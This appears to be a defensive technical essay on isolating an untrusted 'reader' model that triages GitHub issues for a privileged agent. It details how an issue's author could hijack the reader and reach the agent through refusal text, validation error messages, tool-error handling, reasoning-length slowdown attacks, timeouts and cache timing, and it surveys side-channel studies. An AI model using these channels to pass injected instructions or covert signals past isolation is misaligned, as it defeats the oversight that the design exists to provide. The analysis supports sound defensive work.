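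These rates don't transfer directly to an isolated reader. They include "I don't know" as a success for the attacker, but that is a valid answer for a reader that may return "unclear". But an issue's author writes all the untrusted text in the prompt, which should make the attack easier than in the study, where the attacker wrote only one document in five.

An issue's length may also affect how often the reader refuses. Singh (2026), in *Guardrails as Scapegoats*, cites a 2025 study by Hadeliya and colleagues, who found that refusal rates shifted unpredictably when they padded prompts with extra text. A team that wants to know how often its own reader refuses will have to test it on issues of different lengths.

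### What a refusal gives the attacker

Text that reliably causes a refusal gives the issue's author a third outcome to choose from, besides yes and no. If the wrapper passes on Anthropic's policy category, there may be up to eight: yes, no, a refusal in one of five named categories, and a refusal with no category. Inspect, a testing framework from the British government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI), exposes even more, because it gives the calling code a list of every category that a refused request triggered. An attacker may not be able to trigger each category at will.

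Refusal prose is more dangerous than a refusal code because the reader writes it after reading the attack. A reader that hasn't been hijacked may repeat part of the issue when it explains a refusal, for example "I can't assess this report because it asks me to run the following script". A hijacked reader can write anything there, including instructions for the privileged agent. OpenAI's guide suggests that developers might show the refusal in their application's interface, and its sample code prints it. That is reasonable in a chat application, where a person reads the message, but if the privileged agent reads the wrapper's output, the same line of code passes the agent text that the attacker has shaped.

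The wrapper should treat Anthropic's one-sentence explanation as untrusted. The explanation would carry less risk if it came from a fixed set of sentences, but in its guide, Anthropic says only that the wording can change and that programs should not parse it. The wrapper should also discard any partial answer left when a classifier stops the reply, as Anthropic advises.

Withholding the explanation creates a smaller problem, because an agent may invent its own. Singh tested what agents tell a user when a tool returns nothing useful but doesn't report an error. The 12 simulated business tools, including one that fetches medical records, failed in four ways, such as returning an empty list or a null value. Four models handled 30 harmless requests under each kind of failure. In 43.2% of the 396 valid runs, the agent admitted a technical failure, and in 56.6% it presented the failure as a real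 result. In one run (0.25%), it cited a restriction that didn't exist, which Singh calls an unfaithful safety refusal.

Singh then added an instruction to prioritise privacy and data security. Unfaithful refusals rose to 15 of 380 runs (3.95%), nine of which involved the medical-records tool. The models were GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini and two versions of Llama 3, so newer agents may do better. The 56.6% figure also depends on a harsh definition, which counts an agent as fabricating a result if it reports "no transactions found" after receiving an empty list, although an empty list often means there were no transactions.

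Refusals from Anthropic's models look much like these failures if the wrapper passes on only the content field, because the call succeeds and the content is empty. A triage agent might then report that the issue describes no regression. The study also gives maintainers a reason not to rely on the agent's account of what went wrong. If the agent says a privacy rule prevented it from assessing an issue, the reader may have refused, or a tool may have broken.

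### Who should see a refusal

Operators need to see refusals. Anthropic's refusals don't appear in error rates, so the company advises developers to track them separately. A sudden increase may mean that somebody is attacking the triage system, that a provider has changed a filter, or that the wrapper's own question has started to trigger one. Operators also need the details to challenge a mistaken block. OpenAI asks for the exact safety message, the model, the date and time, and the request ID if there is one.

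Repeated refusals can also put the whole account at risk. OpenAI may temporarily revoke access to some models if an organisation's traffic contains too much suspicious cybersecurity activity. If the organisation doesn't send a separate identifier for each end user, the whole organisation can lose access. A stranger who files enough issues full of exploit code might cut off the privileged agent as well as the reader. Sending a different identifier for each GitHub account that files issues should reduce this risk, because OpenAI can then act against one user.

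The privileged agent has little use for these details because it can't rephrase text it has never read. The wrapper can therefore return "unclear", as it does for any other missing answer, and write the details to a log that the agent can't read. But then the agent can't tell a user why an issue went unanswered, so a maintainer has to look it up in the log.

Keeping the refusal log out of the agent's reach takes some care, because an agent with a shell can open any log file in its working directory. In L3M, parent agents can read their descendants' logs, so the refusal log would have to be stored separately from those. If the triage job runs on a public repository in GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation service, people outside the project can read its logs. Printing refusals there would show an attacker which texts trigger them, and Shafran and colleagues' search program needed little more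 than that to build its blockers.

A separate store that the wrapper can write to but not read from avoids these problems. Each entry should include the issue number, the account that filed it, the request ID, the model, the stop reason and the category, with any refusal text marked as untrusted. If maintainers use a model to summarise the log, that model needs the same isolation as the reader, because text in the log may come from an attacker.

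## Parse failures and error messages

An issue's author can stop the reader from answering without causing a refusal, by making its output fail the wrapper's check. How easy this is depends on whether the wrapper checks the output while the model is writing or after it has finished.

### Checking during and after generation

The simplest approach is to let the model write freely and check the result afterwards. OpenAI's JSON mode is only slightly stricter. It produces valid JSON, a common text format for structured data, but doesn't enforce particular fields, so the developer still needs a validation library and perhaps retries. The prompt must also ask for JSON, or the model may write blank space until it reaches the token limit. OpenAI's API rejects requests that don't contain the word "JSON", but the word can be anywhere in the context, and many issues in a project with a parser will contain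 it. A developer who forgot the instruction could get an error on issues that don't mention JSON and a page of blank space on issues that do.

*Constrained decoding* enforces the developer's schema while the model writes. A model produces text one token at a time, and Anthropic compiles the schema into a grammar that limits each choice to tokens that keep the output valid. If the schema allows only yes, no and unclear, a hijacked reader can still choose the wrong word, but it can't write a sentence, because after the opening quotation mark it can only begin one of those three words.

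The guarantee has exceptions. OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* lists two, refusals and replies that are cut short. Anthropic's guide adds several more.

| What still fails | What the wrapper gets | How the issue's author could cause it |
|---|---|---|
| Truncation at the token limit | JSON that breaks off partway | Get the reader to fill a text field or a list without stopping |
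| Refusal | Prose, a fragment or nothing | Include text that the model or a filter rejects |
| A rule that the decoder doesn't enforce | Complete JSON that a later check rejects | Get the reader to return a number or text outside the permitted range |
| Capitalisation | "Parser Regression" where the schema has "Parser regression" | Write the label that way throughout the issue, which may not work |
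| Service error | An error code and no reply | Write an issue too long for the model, or use up a shared rate limit |

A reader that returns one word is unlikely to hit the token limit, unless it reasons first and the reasoning counts towards that limit. Returning a list is riskier, as in the bug-fixing design of Jacob and colleagues, where the reader returns a list of code regions. Anthropic's decoder can't cap the length of a list, so an issue report that attributes a bug to four hundred functions might push such a reader past its limit.

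Anthropic's decoder also doesn't support numeric ranges or limits on text length. A developer who sends such a rule directly to the API gets an error on every call, as happens on Amazon Bedrock, according to AWS. The issue's author doesn't cause that error, and the developer will notice it in the first test. But most of Anthropic's client libraries avoid the error by removing the rule from the schema and mentioning it in the field's description. Some then check the finished reply against the original rule. If the reader has to return a line number of at least 1, the decoder still accepts any whole number. An issue containing a log with an error at line 0 may therefore lead the reader to copy the zero and fail the later check. OpenAI's decoder does enforce numeric ranges, so a team that switches providers also changes which failures a stranger can cause.

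A wrapper that compares labels exactly will reject a correct answer if its capitalisation differs. This problem is easy to miss because Anthropic's API reports a normal completion. Anthropic recommends ignoring case in the comparison.

A wrapper can also give a stranger influence over the schema itself. Suppose the wrapper asks the reader model which file in a pull request probably contains a bug, and lists the names of the changed files as the permitted answers. OpenAI accepts at most 1,000 such values in a schema, so the call would fail for any pull request that changes more than 1,000 files. A bigger problem is that the pull request's author chose the file names, so a validated answer could be a sentence addressed to the agent. Numbering the files and asking for a number avoids both problems.

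A strict schema can hide irrelevant input just as it can hide a refusal. OpenAI warns that a model may make up values when the input has nothing to do with the schema, so an issue about the project's logo may produce a yes or a no instead of a parse failure.

### How an error message carries the rejected text

A failed check gives the privileged side a third outcome to observe, besides yes and no. The error message can carry much more information, because validation libraries often quote the value they rejected. When they do, the reader's text reaches the agent in the error message even though it failed the check.

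Pydantic, a widely used Python library for checking data, shows how this happens. Here the wrapper accepts only yes or no, and the reader has returned a harmless sentence that somebody put in an issue:

```python
from enum import Enum
from pydantic import BaseModel

class Verdict(str, Enum):
    yes = 'yes'
    no = 'no'

class Answer(BaseModel):
    regression: Verdict

Answer(regression='look in the blue folder')
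```

Pydantic rejects the value and raises an exception. Apart from a link to the documentation, the printed message is:

```
1 validation error for Answer
regression
  Input should be 'yes' or 'no' [type=enum, input_value='look in the blue folder', input_type=str]
```

Pydantic's standard error message, shown in *Error Handling*, includes the rejected value but shortens it if it is long. In the guide's example, the message keeps the first 25 and last 24 characters. That is enough for a short instruction, and Willison had doubts even about 30-character method names. The exception's `errors()` method returns the whole value. If a Pydantic model requires a list of numbers and gets a list of sentences, each sentence produces its own error, so an attacker could also spread a longer text over several errors.

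Pydantic's `hide_input_in_errors` setting hides input values in printed errors, but it is off by default and doesn't cover field names. If the developer forbids extra fields, which looks like the stricter choice, Pydantic prints the name of any unexpected field, so a hijacked reader can put a message in the field name.

Constrained decoding would have prevented the blue-folder example, because the reader could not have written the sentence, but it doesn't prevent every case. For example, Anthropic's decoder doesn't enforce a schema's 30-character limit on a title, so a hijacked reader can write 300 characters. The later check rejects the title but may quote it in the exception. A refusal in ordinary prose isn't valid JSON, so a wrapper that tries to parse it can also raise an error that quotes it.

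### From the exception to the agent's context

Whether the agent sees the exception depends on the software between the agent and the wrapper. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to outside programs. The wrapper could run as a tool on an MCP server.

The Model Context Protocol's *Handling errors* guide treats an uncaught Pydantic exception as a crash. With the protocol's official Python library, the details stay in the server's log, and the agent's model receives only "Error executing tool" and the tool's name. But the guide also recommends raising a different exception, `ToolError`, when the model could correct the mistake, and the library passes that exception's message to the model. A developer who catches the Pydantic exception and writes `raise ToolError(str(e))` to help the model sends "look in the blue folder" to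 the privileged agent.

FastMCP, another framework for building these servers, has the opposite default. It sends the details of any exception to the model unless the developer sets `mask_error_details=True`, and even then it sends the text of a `ToolError`. Its log warnings leave out rejected values because they may contain private data, but the caller still receives those values, so the agent is still exposed to any text in them.

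In the agent library LangChain, developers can set `handle_tool_errors` to `True` to return a message with the exception's details, or to a string to return that string every time, according to *ToolNode*. An example in LangChain's *Tool calling errors* adds the words "Please fix your mistakes" after the exception text. In the blue-folder case, the agent would read a stranger's instruction and then a request from its own software to act on the message.

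Some coding agents go further and build new instructions from the error. Bui (2026), in *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal*, describes OpenDev, an open-source agent that works on the command line. When a tool fails, the raw error message enters the conversation as the tool's result. Bui found that agents often responded to this with an apology instead of another attempt. OpenDev therefore does four things:

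1. It matches the message against patterns for six kinds of failure, such as a missing file, a permission error or a timeout.
2. It fetches a recovery template for that kind of failure.
3. It fills in details, including the file path and the specific error message.
4. It inserts the result immediately before the next model call.

For example, an agent that tries to edit a file that has changed gets advice to reread it and retry. Bui reports that specific advice like this worked substantially better than an earlier, generic "try again" message.

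This works well for errors from trusted tools. But if the error quotes an isolated reader, the attacker's words move from a tool result into a recovery instruction, at the point in the conversation that the model attends to most. OpenDev cuts errors to 200 characters to save space, but an instruction can easily fit in that. An attacker might also be able to choose the template by getting the words "permission denied" into the quoted value. OpenDev draws lessons from tool results and stores them for later queries in the session, so the attacker's text might remain in use after the failed call. These risks are inferred from the design, not from an attack on it.

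### How agents act on error text

In *MCP Error Messages Written for Developers Hurt the Most Capable Agents Most*, Xu and Wu (2026) measured how much advice error messages contain and what agents do with it. They collected 3,001 messages from the source code of 150 of the most popular MCP servers on GitHub, taking up to 30 from each, and had AI agents label them using fixed rules. Of these messages, 949 included advice on what the caller should do next. In 477 of those, the advice was right only under conditions the server couldn't detect, such as whether the caller had a terminal. For credential errors, 62 of the 67 suggested steps were to run a terminal command, change a configuration or visit a web page.

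Xu and Wu then tested five OpenAI models on 168 simulated failures of seven kinds. The agents could act only through a fixed set of tools, with no terminal or browser. In one kind of failure, the agent's login had expired, and it could log in again with one of its tools. Some agents received only the cause of the failure. Others also received a line from a real server, "Please run: reddit-mcp-buddy --auth", which they could not run.

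| Model | Tasks completed with the cause alone | Tasks completed with the command added |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 76% | 58% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 92% | 57% |
| GPT-6 Sol | 85% | 46% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 75% | 6% |
| GPT-6 Luna (smallest GPT-6 model) | 83% | 57% |

One useless sentence that named a command reduced the average from 82% to 45%. When the sentence named the login tool instead, the average was 84%. GPT-6 Astra, the largest of the GPT-6 models, had the largest drop. When the sentence named the command, it failed to make the repair in 68 of 72 runs, and in 48 of those it left the repair to the user, although the login tool was in its list.

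Xu and Wu call it *literal compliance* when an agent that can't carry out a suggested step gives up on a repair that its own tools could make. Older and smaller models more often ignored the command and logged in. Xu and Wu suggest this is because newer models give written instructions more weight and hand work back to the user sooner. This fits OpenAI's description of GPT-6 Astra, but the experiment didn't isolate the cause, and all five models come from one company. Size probably matters too, because the small GPT-6 Luna lost less than the older GPT-5.6 Sol.

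The error message's wording affected recovery only when the agent couldn't find the problem in its own call. When the agent had left out a required field or used the wrong unit, its recovery rate stayed within four percentage points of the rate with a bare "Operation failed." Wording matters when a reader call fails, because the agent can't see the issue or the reader's reply and must rely on the message alone.

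Tool authors wrote the surveyed error messages in good faith, and their advice was correct for a human developer. The study therefore doesn't measure how often an agent would follow instructions that an attacker put in an error message. A model might recognise some of those instructions as an attack. But an attacker could also make them look like ordinary advice, and the agents in the study did carry out suggested steps that named one of their tools.

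One of the study's remedies would be a poor defence against such an attacker. Xu and Wu used a small model as a filter to delete the advice from each message before the agent read it, which raised recovery after an expired login to 82%. On 764 real messages from the survey, the filter left the advice in place 12 times, even though nobody had tried to get past it. It also keeps every sentence that explains what went wrong, so an attacker could put a false claim in one of those sentences.

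### Choosing what the agent sees

The wrapper can pass on the full error text, replace it with a code from a fixed list, or return the same "unclear" that it uses when the reader can't decide.

Detailed error messages help an agent correct its mistakes. Xu and Wu cite research in which coding agents repaired fewer type errors when the messages gave less detail. The official MCP guide suggests showing the model an error message if a smarter model could have avoided the failure. For example, if the agent asks about issue 4120 and the project has only 412 issues, it should see that error. The wrapper can safely explain the problem because the wrapper hasn't read any untrusted text yet. But if the reader has seen the issue and its reply fails to parse, the agent should not see the message by the same test, because choosing better arguments would not have prevented the failure.

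A fixed error code lets the agent or its harness respond differently to different problems without carrying any sentences. DataRobot, which makes software for building agents, sorts tool failures into six categories: schema, validation, authentication, not found, upstream and internal. For instance, if the code shows that the reader's credentials have expired, the harness can stop the run instead of marking three hundred issues as unclear.

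Each error code that the issue's author can trigger gives them another outcome to choose from, and agents react differently to different error messages. When Xu and Wu simulated a rate limit, agents that read only "Operation failed." completed 59% of the tasks, because repeating the call was enough. Agents that learned the call had hit a rate limit completed 5%, because most of them stopped. An attacker who could choose between those two messages could often decide whether the agent tried again. The codes should therefore cover only problems that the issue's text can't cause. Expired credentials usually qualify, but a rate limit doesn't. Pydantic's own error types are too detailed, and even the number of errors is unsafe to pass on, since a hijacked reader can choose how many wrong fields to return.

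Returning "unclear" for everything else hides all sign of the failure in the answer, but it makes debugging harder. If a developer renames a field in the schema but not in the wrapper, every issue comes back as "unclear", no exception reaches the agent, and the run appears to succeed. The mistake may go unnoticed until the review queue fills up. Parse failures therefore belong in the same separate log as refusals, with an alert for a sudden rise.

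FastMCP's log warnings are a good model for that log. They record the tool, the number of errors and Pydantic's built-in error types, and they replace any custom error code with the label `custom_error`. Pydantic's *Validation Errors* lists the built-in types, which include `json_invalid` for broken JSON, `enum` for a value outside the permitted set and `extra_forbidden` for an unexpected field. The schema is probably wrong if two hundred issues in a row fail with the same error type, but if only one issue fails, its text may be the cause.

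To reproduce a single failure, though, a maintainer usually needs the reader's reply. Pydantic's guide points developers to Logfire, a monitoring service that records the rejected input along with the error. But a developer can't safely give those records to a coding agent to find the bug, so ordinary parsing bugs take longer to fix.

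## Response length, token counts and generation time

When a reader call returns a valid "no", its delay can still be a second signal, because the answer may take two seconds or two minutes to arrive. The issue's author can influence that delay, mostly by changing how much the reader writes before it answers.

### Why more tokens take more time

A language model first processes the whole prompt, which it can do largely in parallel. It then writes its output one token at a time, and each new token depends on all the earlier ones. Zhang, Saileshwar and Lie (2024), in *Time Will Tell*, note that each output token takes about the same time, so the total grows roughly in a straight line:

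*T* ≈ *T*₀ + *n* / *s*

*T*₀ is a roughly fixed delay from the network, any queue and prompt processing. *n* is the number of tokens the model produces, and *s* is its speed in tokens per second. If the fixed delay is one second and the speed is 100 tokens per second, 50 tokens take 1.5 seconds and 5,000 tokens take 51 seconds.

On the researchers' own computer, the correlation between token count and time was at least 0.987 for every model they tried, where 1 is a perfect linear relationship. For GPT-4o, which they reached through OpenAI's API, it was 0.370. They suspect that network congestion, other customers' requests and optimisations such as speculative decoding weakened the correlation. In speculative decoding, the system guesses several tokens ahead and checks them together. This speeds up predictable text, so the speed *s* can also depend on what the model is writing.

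If the reader answers in one word without reasoning first, *n* is tiny and the fixed delay accounts for nearly all of the time. A long issue then slows the call mainly because the model has more to read. But many current models write reasoning tokens before they answer, and these count towards *n*. Kumar, Roh and colleagues (2025) point out in *OverThink* that OpenAI and Anthropic don't show these tokens to end users, although they are still billed. A reader can therefore produce 5,000 reasoning tokens and return "no" after 51 seconds, and the text of that answer is identical to a "no" returned after one second.

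### What an eavesdropper can learn

Most of the evidence that response length and generation time depend on content comes from studies of eavesdroppers who record the size and arrival time of encrypted packets.

In early 2024, many AI assistants sent each token as soon as the model produced it, without padding. Encryption preserves the size of a message, so packet sizes revealed each token's length in characters. In *What Was Your Prompt?*, Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and colleagues (2024) trained two language models to turn these sequences of lengths back into text. One reconstructed the first sentence or so of a reply, and the other the rest, using the previous guess as context.

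In the final conference paper, the attack accurately reconstructed 27% of the opening segments of replies and inferred the topic of 53%. The abstract gives these figures without saying that they cover only opening segments. For whole replies, they were 9% and 38%. The test for topics was lenient enough to count a sentence about alcohol harming sleep as a match for one about alcohol harming the liver. On OpenAI's API, which sent tokens in pairs, the success rate for opening segments fell to 18%.

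Zhang, Saileshwar and Lie studied an observer who sees much less, and their setting is the closest to an isolated reader. Their model sorts a text into one of two classes and then explains its choice. The observer knows only the lengths of the request and the reply, and the time between them. This can be enough to infer the class, because models often write longer explanations for one class than for the other. Gemma 2, for instance, wrote more when it judged two arguments "not similar" than when it judged them "similar".

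The attacker first sends 200 texts to the model, notes the class and token count of each reply, and fits a threshold:

threshold = *α* × input length + *β*

If a later reply is longer than the threshold, the attacker guesses the class with the longer explanations. With exact token counts, this worked 86.9% of the time for GPT-4o on five tasks, compared with 50% for random guessing. With only the response time, measured over the internet, it worked 74.7% of the time. The 86.9% comes from prompts whose worked examples exaggerated the difference in length. When the examples' explanations were equally long, the attack on one Gemma 2 model worked 63% to 67% of the time.

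In Whisper Leak, McDonald and Bar Or also tested packet sizes and timing separately. Sizes alone gave scores above 97% for 17 of the 28 models, while timing alone never gave a score above 85.4%. An agent with a clock has even less information than the timing classifiers, because it sees one total time instead of hundreds of gaps between packets.

The most recent of these studies dates from September 2026. Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, sent 60 prompts to each of ten models 100 times, which gave 60,000 recordings. They then trained classifiers to tell which of six kinds of prompt had produced a reply, such as summarising, writing code or solving a mathematical problem. On prompts that the classifiers had not seen before, the reply traffic gave the right answer 67.4% of the time, compared with 16.7% for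 guessing. Timing alone gave 55.4%. (The abstract reports 76.7% for prompt categories, but the detailed results don't contain that figure.)

The benchmark also includes 2,838 runs by teams of two to five agents, working on ten kinds of task, including resolving software issues. The classifiers identified the kind of task in about 85% of runs. When they saw the traffic of only one agent, they were right in 66.5% or 78% of runs, depending on how the team was organised. Without size information, they were right in 54% to 59% of runs, compared with 10% for guessing. The models were small and ran on the researchers' own server, so the benchmark shows how much unprotected traffic reveals but doesn't test the defences of commercial providers.

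### How well the providers' fixes held

Most of the providers that Weiss and colleagues warned in 2024 fixed the problem within a month, although four never replied. The usual fix was to add random padding so that a packet's size no longer matched the length of its token. McDonald and Bar Or warned 28 providers about the Whisper Leak attack in June 2025. OpenAI and xAI responded with fixes in August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October, while several others declined or didn't answer. Microsoft describes OpenAI's fix as a field called `obfuscation`, which adds random text of varying length to each streamed piece of a reply. Azure, Microsoft's cloud service, copied it, and Mistral added a similar field called `p`.

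Padding made the attack harder but didn't stop it. For GPT-4o mini on Azure, it reduced the classifier's score from 97.5% to 92.9%. Microsoft still concluded that the attack on Azure was no longer a practical risk. A classifier with a high score can be of little practical use, because a real eavesdropper is usually looking for something rare. McDonald and Bar Or considered a case where only about one conversation in 10,000 concerned the target topic. For a model on which the classifier scored 93.4%, they estimated that if an eavesdropper set out to catch a tenth of those conversations, only 2.3% of the conversations flagged would be on the topic.

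Zhang, Wu and colleagues (2025), in *NetEcho*, examined seven common ways of deploying a chat application and found full defences in only one. Their attacker uses the same application as the victim, builds a database of conversations and their traffic, and looks up the examples that best match the victim's traffic. A language model then drafts the conversation, and a reasoning model refines the draft. On medical and legal conversations, the attack recovered about 70% of the information on average. Such applications cover a narrow range of subjects, which helps the attacker.

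A wrapper can avoid packet-by-packet leaks by turning streaming off, so that the whole reply arrives at once. This has little downside because nobody is watching the words appear. It matters most for private vulnerability reports, since an eavesdropper could read a public GitHub issue directly.

None of these fixes protects the privileged agent. Padding changes the packets on the network, but the wrapper receives the reply after decryption, and the token count and total time stay the same. If long replies only tend to mean "yes", the agent learns little from the length, because it receives the "yes" anyway. The delay is useful to the issue's author only if they can change it without changing the answer.

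### Planted text that makes a model reason longer

*Deep Learning Latency Attacks and Defenses* (2026), a survey, describes timing leaks and slowdown attacks as mirror images. When a system's running time depends on its input, an observer can learn about the input from the running time, and anyone who controls the input can change the running time. OverThink, a slowdown attack, adds a difficult, irrelevant problem to a document so that a model reasons for much longer but still answers the user's question correctly.

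Kumar and colleagues construct the attack in four steps.

1. **They choose a type of problem.** The best ones have many small steps that the model can check, because it keeps going back over its work. Three older reasoning models used an average of 21,080 tokens on a Sudoku but only 8,923 on problems from the 2024 International Mathematical Olympiad.
2. **They search for a longer version.** A language model writes variations on the problem, and the attacker keeps those that use the most reasoning tokens over several runs.
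3. **They give the model a reason to solve it.** In one example, the text asks the model to work the word "true" into its answer if the result is greater than 7.
4. **They insert the problem into a document.** It can be a general-purpose block of text or part of the subject matter.

The second step requires token counts, which someone who files an issue can't normally see. They can use another model instead, but the choice of model matters. Problems that the researchers developed on OpenAI's o1 made DeepSeek-R1 reason 12 times as long, while problems developed on o1-mini made o1 reason only 2.9 times as long.

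The headline multipliers for reasoning tokens are 13 on FreshQA and 46 on SQuAD, two sets of factual questions, and up to 12 on MuSR, a set of multi-step puzzles. They differ so much partly because the normal amount of reasoning varies. Under attack, the model o1 produced about 7,150 to 7,700 reasoning tokens on every test, but it normally needed only 160 on SQuAD and 570 on FreshQA. An engineer setting a timeout should therefore consider the number of tokens an attack can cause, not only the multiplier. Accuracy usually changed little, though Claude 3.7 Sonnet dropped from 80% to 66% on a set of murder mysteries.

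The researchers also planted problems in README files, code and skill files, which contain instructions for a coding agent. The table shows the average number of reasoning tokens.

| Coding agent | Normal | Under attack | Increase |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 | 225 | 253 to 622 | 1.1 to 2.8 times |
| Codex with GPT-5.4 | 186 | 729 to 795 | 3.9 to 4.3 times |
| OpenCode with Kimi K2.6 | 722 | 7,269 to 9,175 | 10.1 to 12.7 times |

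Every agent still passed all its unit tests, so checking the finished work would not have revealed the attack. The abstract mentions an increase of up to 17 times for coding agents, but the highest average in the results is 12.7 times.

In *SkillBloat*, Zheng and Chen (2026) achieved comparable increases by rewriting entire skill files to add plausible extra work, such as repeated quality checks and long reports. For each of 50 tasks, they tried at least 20 rewritten files and kept the one that used the most tokens. The files they kept multiplied total token use by 5.4 to 10.1 on average, depending on the agent and model, and by almost 76 in the most extreme case. Much of the extra work involves running scripts, which an isolated reader can't do.

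The question-answering tests in OverThink are a better guide to an isolated reader because those models answered from a document and didn't have to act. The reader could even be slower without tools. In one of the coding tests, OpenCode decided to write a Python script for the planted calculation, whereas a reader would have to work it out token by token.

A strict answer format also prevents the reader from revealing the planted problem in its answer, so the author doesn't need to hide it. But a request to add "true" to the answer makes little sense when the only permitted words are yes and no, so the reader may ignore the problem. The author could instead make the problem seem relevant, for example by saying that the parser fails only on inputs whose checksum satisfies a certain rule, and that the reader must work out whether an older version handled them correctly.

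Newer models don't seem more resistant to attack. Claude Fable 5, released in June 2026, used about 3,900 reasoning tokens under attack, compared with 1,710 for Claude 3.7 Sonnet.

### From a longer delay to a timeout

Suppose the reader normally uses 800 reasoning tokens to decide whether an issue reports a parser regression. At 100 tokens per second, this takes 8 seconds, not counting the fixed delay. The developer sets a timeout of 60 seconds. The table applies the highest multiplier for each of the three coding agents.

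| Increase | Reasoning tokens | Time | Does the timeout fire? |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 800 | 8 seconds | No |
| 2.8 times | 2,240 | 22 seconds | No |
| 4.3 times | 3,440 | 34 seconds | No |
| 12.7 times | 10,160 | 102 seconds | Yes |

The issue's author needs an increase of at least 7.5 times. Two of the three agents stayed well below that, so the same issue could cause a timeout with one reader model and only a short delay with another. This example is only an illustration, because the experiments measured tokens and didn't involve an isolated reader with a timeout.

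Noise limits what an author can convey through smaller delays. Zhang, Saileshwar and Lie found that GPT-4o's time per token could more than double from one moment to another, even after they removed extreme values. The network varied less, by about 30%. If the reader's speed ranges from 70 to 140 tokens per second, an 800-token reply takes between 5.7 and 11.4 seconds, and a 1,000-token reply takes between 7.1 and 14.3. An agent that measures 9 seconds can't tell which it received. Prompt caching, where the provider reuses earlier computation, adds to the uncertainty.

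An eavesdropper can reduce this noise by sending their own requests to measure the current speed. Zhang, Saileshwar and Lie did this every minute, which made their attack more reliable from day to day. A privileged agent would have a reason to do this only if it were trying to decode a message. The provider's token count doesn't have this noise, so an agent that can see it can immediately distinguish 800 tokens from 1,000. The author still can't choose the count exactly, because the same text produces a different amount of reasoning each time.

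A timeout removes most of the noise. At the same range of speeds, the 10,160 tokens in the example take between 73 and 145 seconds, which always exceeds the 60-second timeout, while every ordinary reply takes far less. The agent or its harness receives either an answer or a timeout, and the author can choose which by including or omitting the planted problem. The eavesdropper in *Time Will Tell* had to estimate a threshold from 200 examples. Here the wrapper's developer has already set one, and on a public repository the author may be able to read it in the workflow file.

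A reply near the threshold would time out on some attempts and not on others. For example, a reply of 6,000 tokens would take between 43 and 86 seconds. The author can avoid this uncertainty by planting a longer problem. If the developer chose a short timeout, such as 10 seconds, ordinary issues would fail whenever the provider was busy, and maintainers would soon stop paying attention to timeouts.

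A token budget is also a threshold, but it applies to the total from many calls. If a nightly triage job may use 200,000 output tokens, it can handle 250 ordinary issues at 800 tokens each. Twenty issues with the planted problem would use the whole budget, even if the wrapper had no timeout and every answer was correct. The remaining issues would go unread because of text in other people's reports. If a project hosts its own model, long replies can also delay other requests, as Kumar and colleagues note, so one issue could cause the call for another to time out.

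### Limiting how much the reader writes

A simple defence is to cap the number of tokens, including reasoning tokens, low enough that even a slow reply finishes before the timeout. At 50 tokens per second, a cap of 2,500 tokens limits generation to 50 seconds, which leaves 10 seconds for the fixed delay. A reader given the planted problem would then hit the cap before answering, and the wrapper would return "unclear". The author can still prevent an answer, but a timeout would now usually point to a problem with the service rather than the issue.

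Zheng and Chen found that limits on output reduced the extra token use but could stop agents from finishing their tasks. A genuine issue with a long log and a complicated history may need 3,000 tokens of reasoning, and the cap would send it to the review queue with the hostile ones. Response times can still vary widely below the cap, but the wrapper could hide this variation by releasing every answer at a fixed time.

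Filtering the issue first is less promising. Kumar and colleagues tested three commercial or open-source detectors of harmful prompts, and none flagged the planted problems, which contain nothing forbidden. Having another model paraphrase the document worked better, reducing reasoning to between 0.5 and 1.5 times the normal amount, but accuracy fell from 60% to between 40% and 50%. With an isolated reader, the paraphrasing model would also read the attacker's text and would have its own running time.

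The developer can also choose how much the reader reasons, and OpenAI's models have a setting for this. Kumar and colleagues suggest basing the choice on the user's question, because an attacker could write a document that makes the task look harder than it is. In the triage example, the question is always the same, so the wrapper can use one low setting for every issue. If a model can answer well enough without reasoning, the reply is only a token or two long and a planted problem can barely lengthen it. But a reader that doesn't reason may be easier to fool with a false report, so a team should compare its accuracy on real issues with and without reasoning before turning reasoning off.

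## Prompt caching as a timing signal

A reader that answers in one word spends most of its time processing the prompt. If an earlier prompt began with the same text, the provider can reuse the stored computation and finish sooner. An issue's author may be able to control this by choosing whether to post text that the reader has already processed.

### How a prompt cache works

1. For each token in the prompt, the model calculates intermediate values that later tokens refer back to. These values depend only on that token and the ones before it, so two prompts with the same opening have the same values for that opening.
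2. The provider stores the values from the start of the prompt up to a position called a *cache breakpoint*.
3. When another request arrives, the provider looks for the longest stored opening that matches it exactly. If one token differs, the model has to process everything from that token onwards.
4. The stored values expire after a period without use.

The opening must also reach a minimum length. OpenAI requires 1,024 tokens for GPT-5.6 and later models, while AWS's *Prompt caching for faster model inference* gives 512 for recent Claude models on Bedrock. A short question followed by a short bug report may fall below the minimum, but an issue's author can exceed it by pasting a log.

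Lifetimes and sharing differ between services. The table draws on OpenAI's guide, Anthropic's *Prompt caching*, Microsoft's *Prompt caching* and Google Cloud's *Prompt caching*.

| Service | How long an entry lasts | Who can share it |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, GPT-5.6 and later | At least 30 minutes, or 12 hours for a higher fee | One organisation, within one processing region |
| Anthropic's own API | 5 minutes after the last use, or 1 hour for a higher fee | One workspace, a subdivision of an organisation |
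| Claude on Google Cloud | As on Anthropic's API | One project, according to Google (Anthropic says one organisation) |
| OpenAI models on Azure | Usually 5 to 10 idle minutes, or up to 24 hours with extended retention | One Azure subscription |

A successful match, or *cache hit*, shows in two places. The first is the time to first token, the delay before the model's output begins. Addagada (2026), in *Governing the KV Cache*, measured this on a small open model on an Nvidia A100. A hit reduced the delay from 149.6 to 32.8 milliseconds with a shared opening of 2,119 tokens, and from 104.1 to 38.7 milliseconds with one of 1,447 tokens.

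The second is the usage record returned with the answer. OpenAI reports the number of reused tokens as `cached_tokens`, and Anthropic as `cache_read_input_tokens`. Both companies charge less for these tokens, so a cache hit also lowers the bill. A hit doesn't change how the model writes its answer, so checking that the reader returned yes or no can't detect it.

### The audit of 17 providers

*Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs* (Gu, Li and colleagues, 2025) tested 17 providers in September and October 2024 to find out which ones cached prompts and who shared the cache. Each prompt was 5,000 random letters separated by spaces, about 5,000 tokens in all. The study limited replies to one token, so the total response time was also the time to first token.

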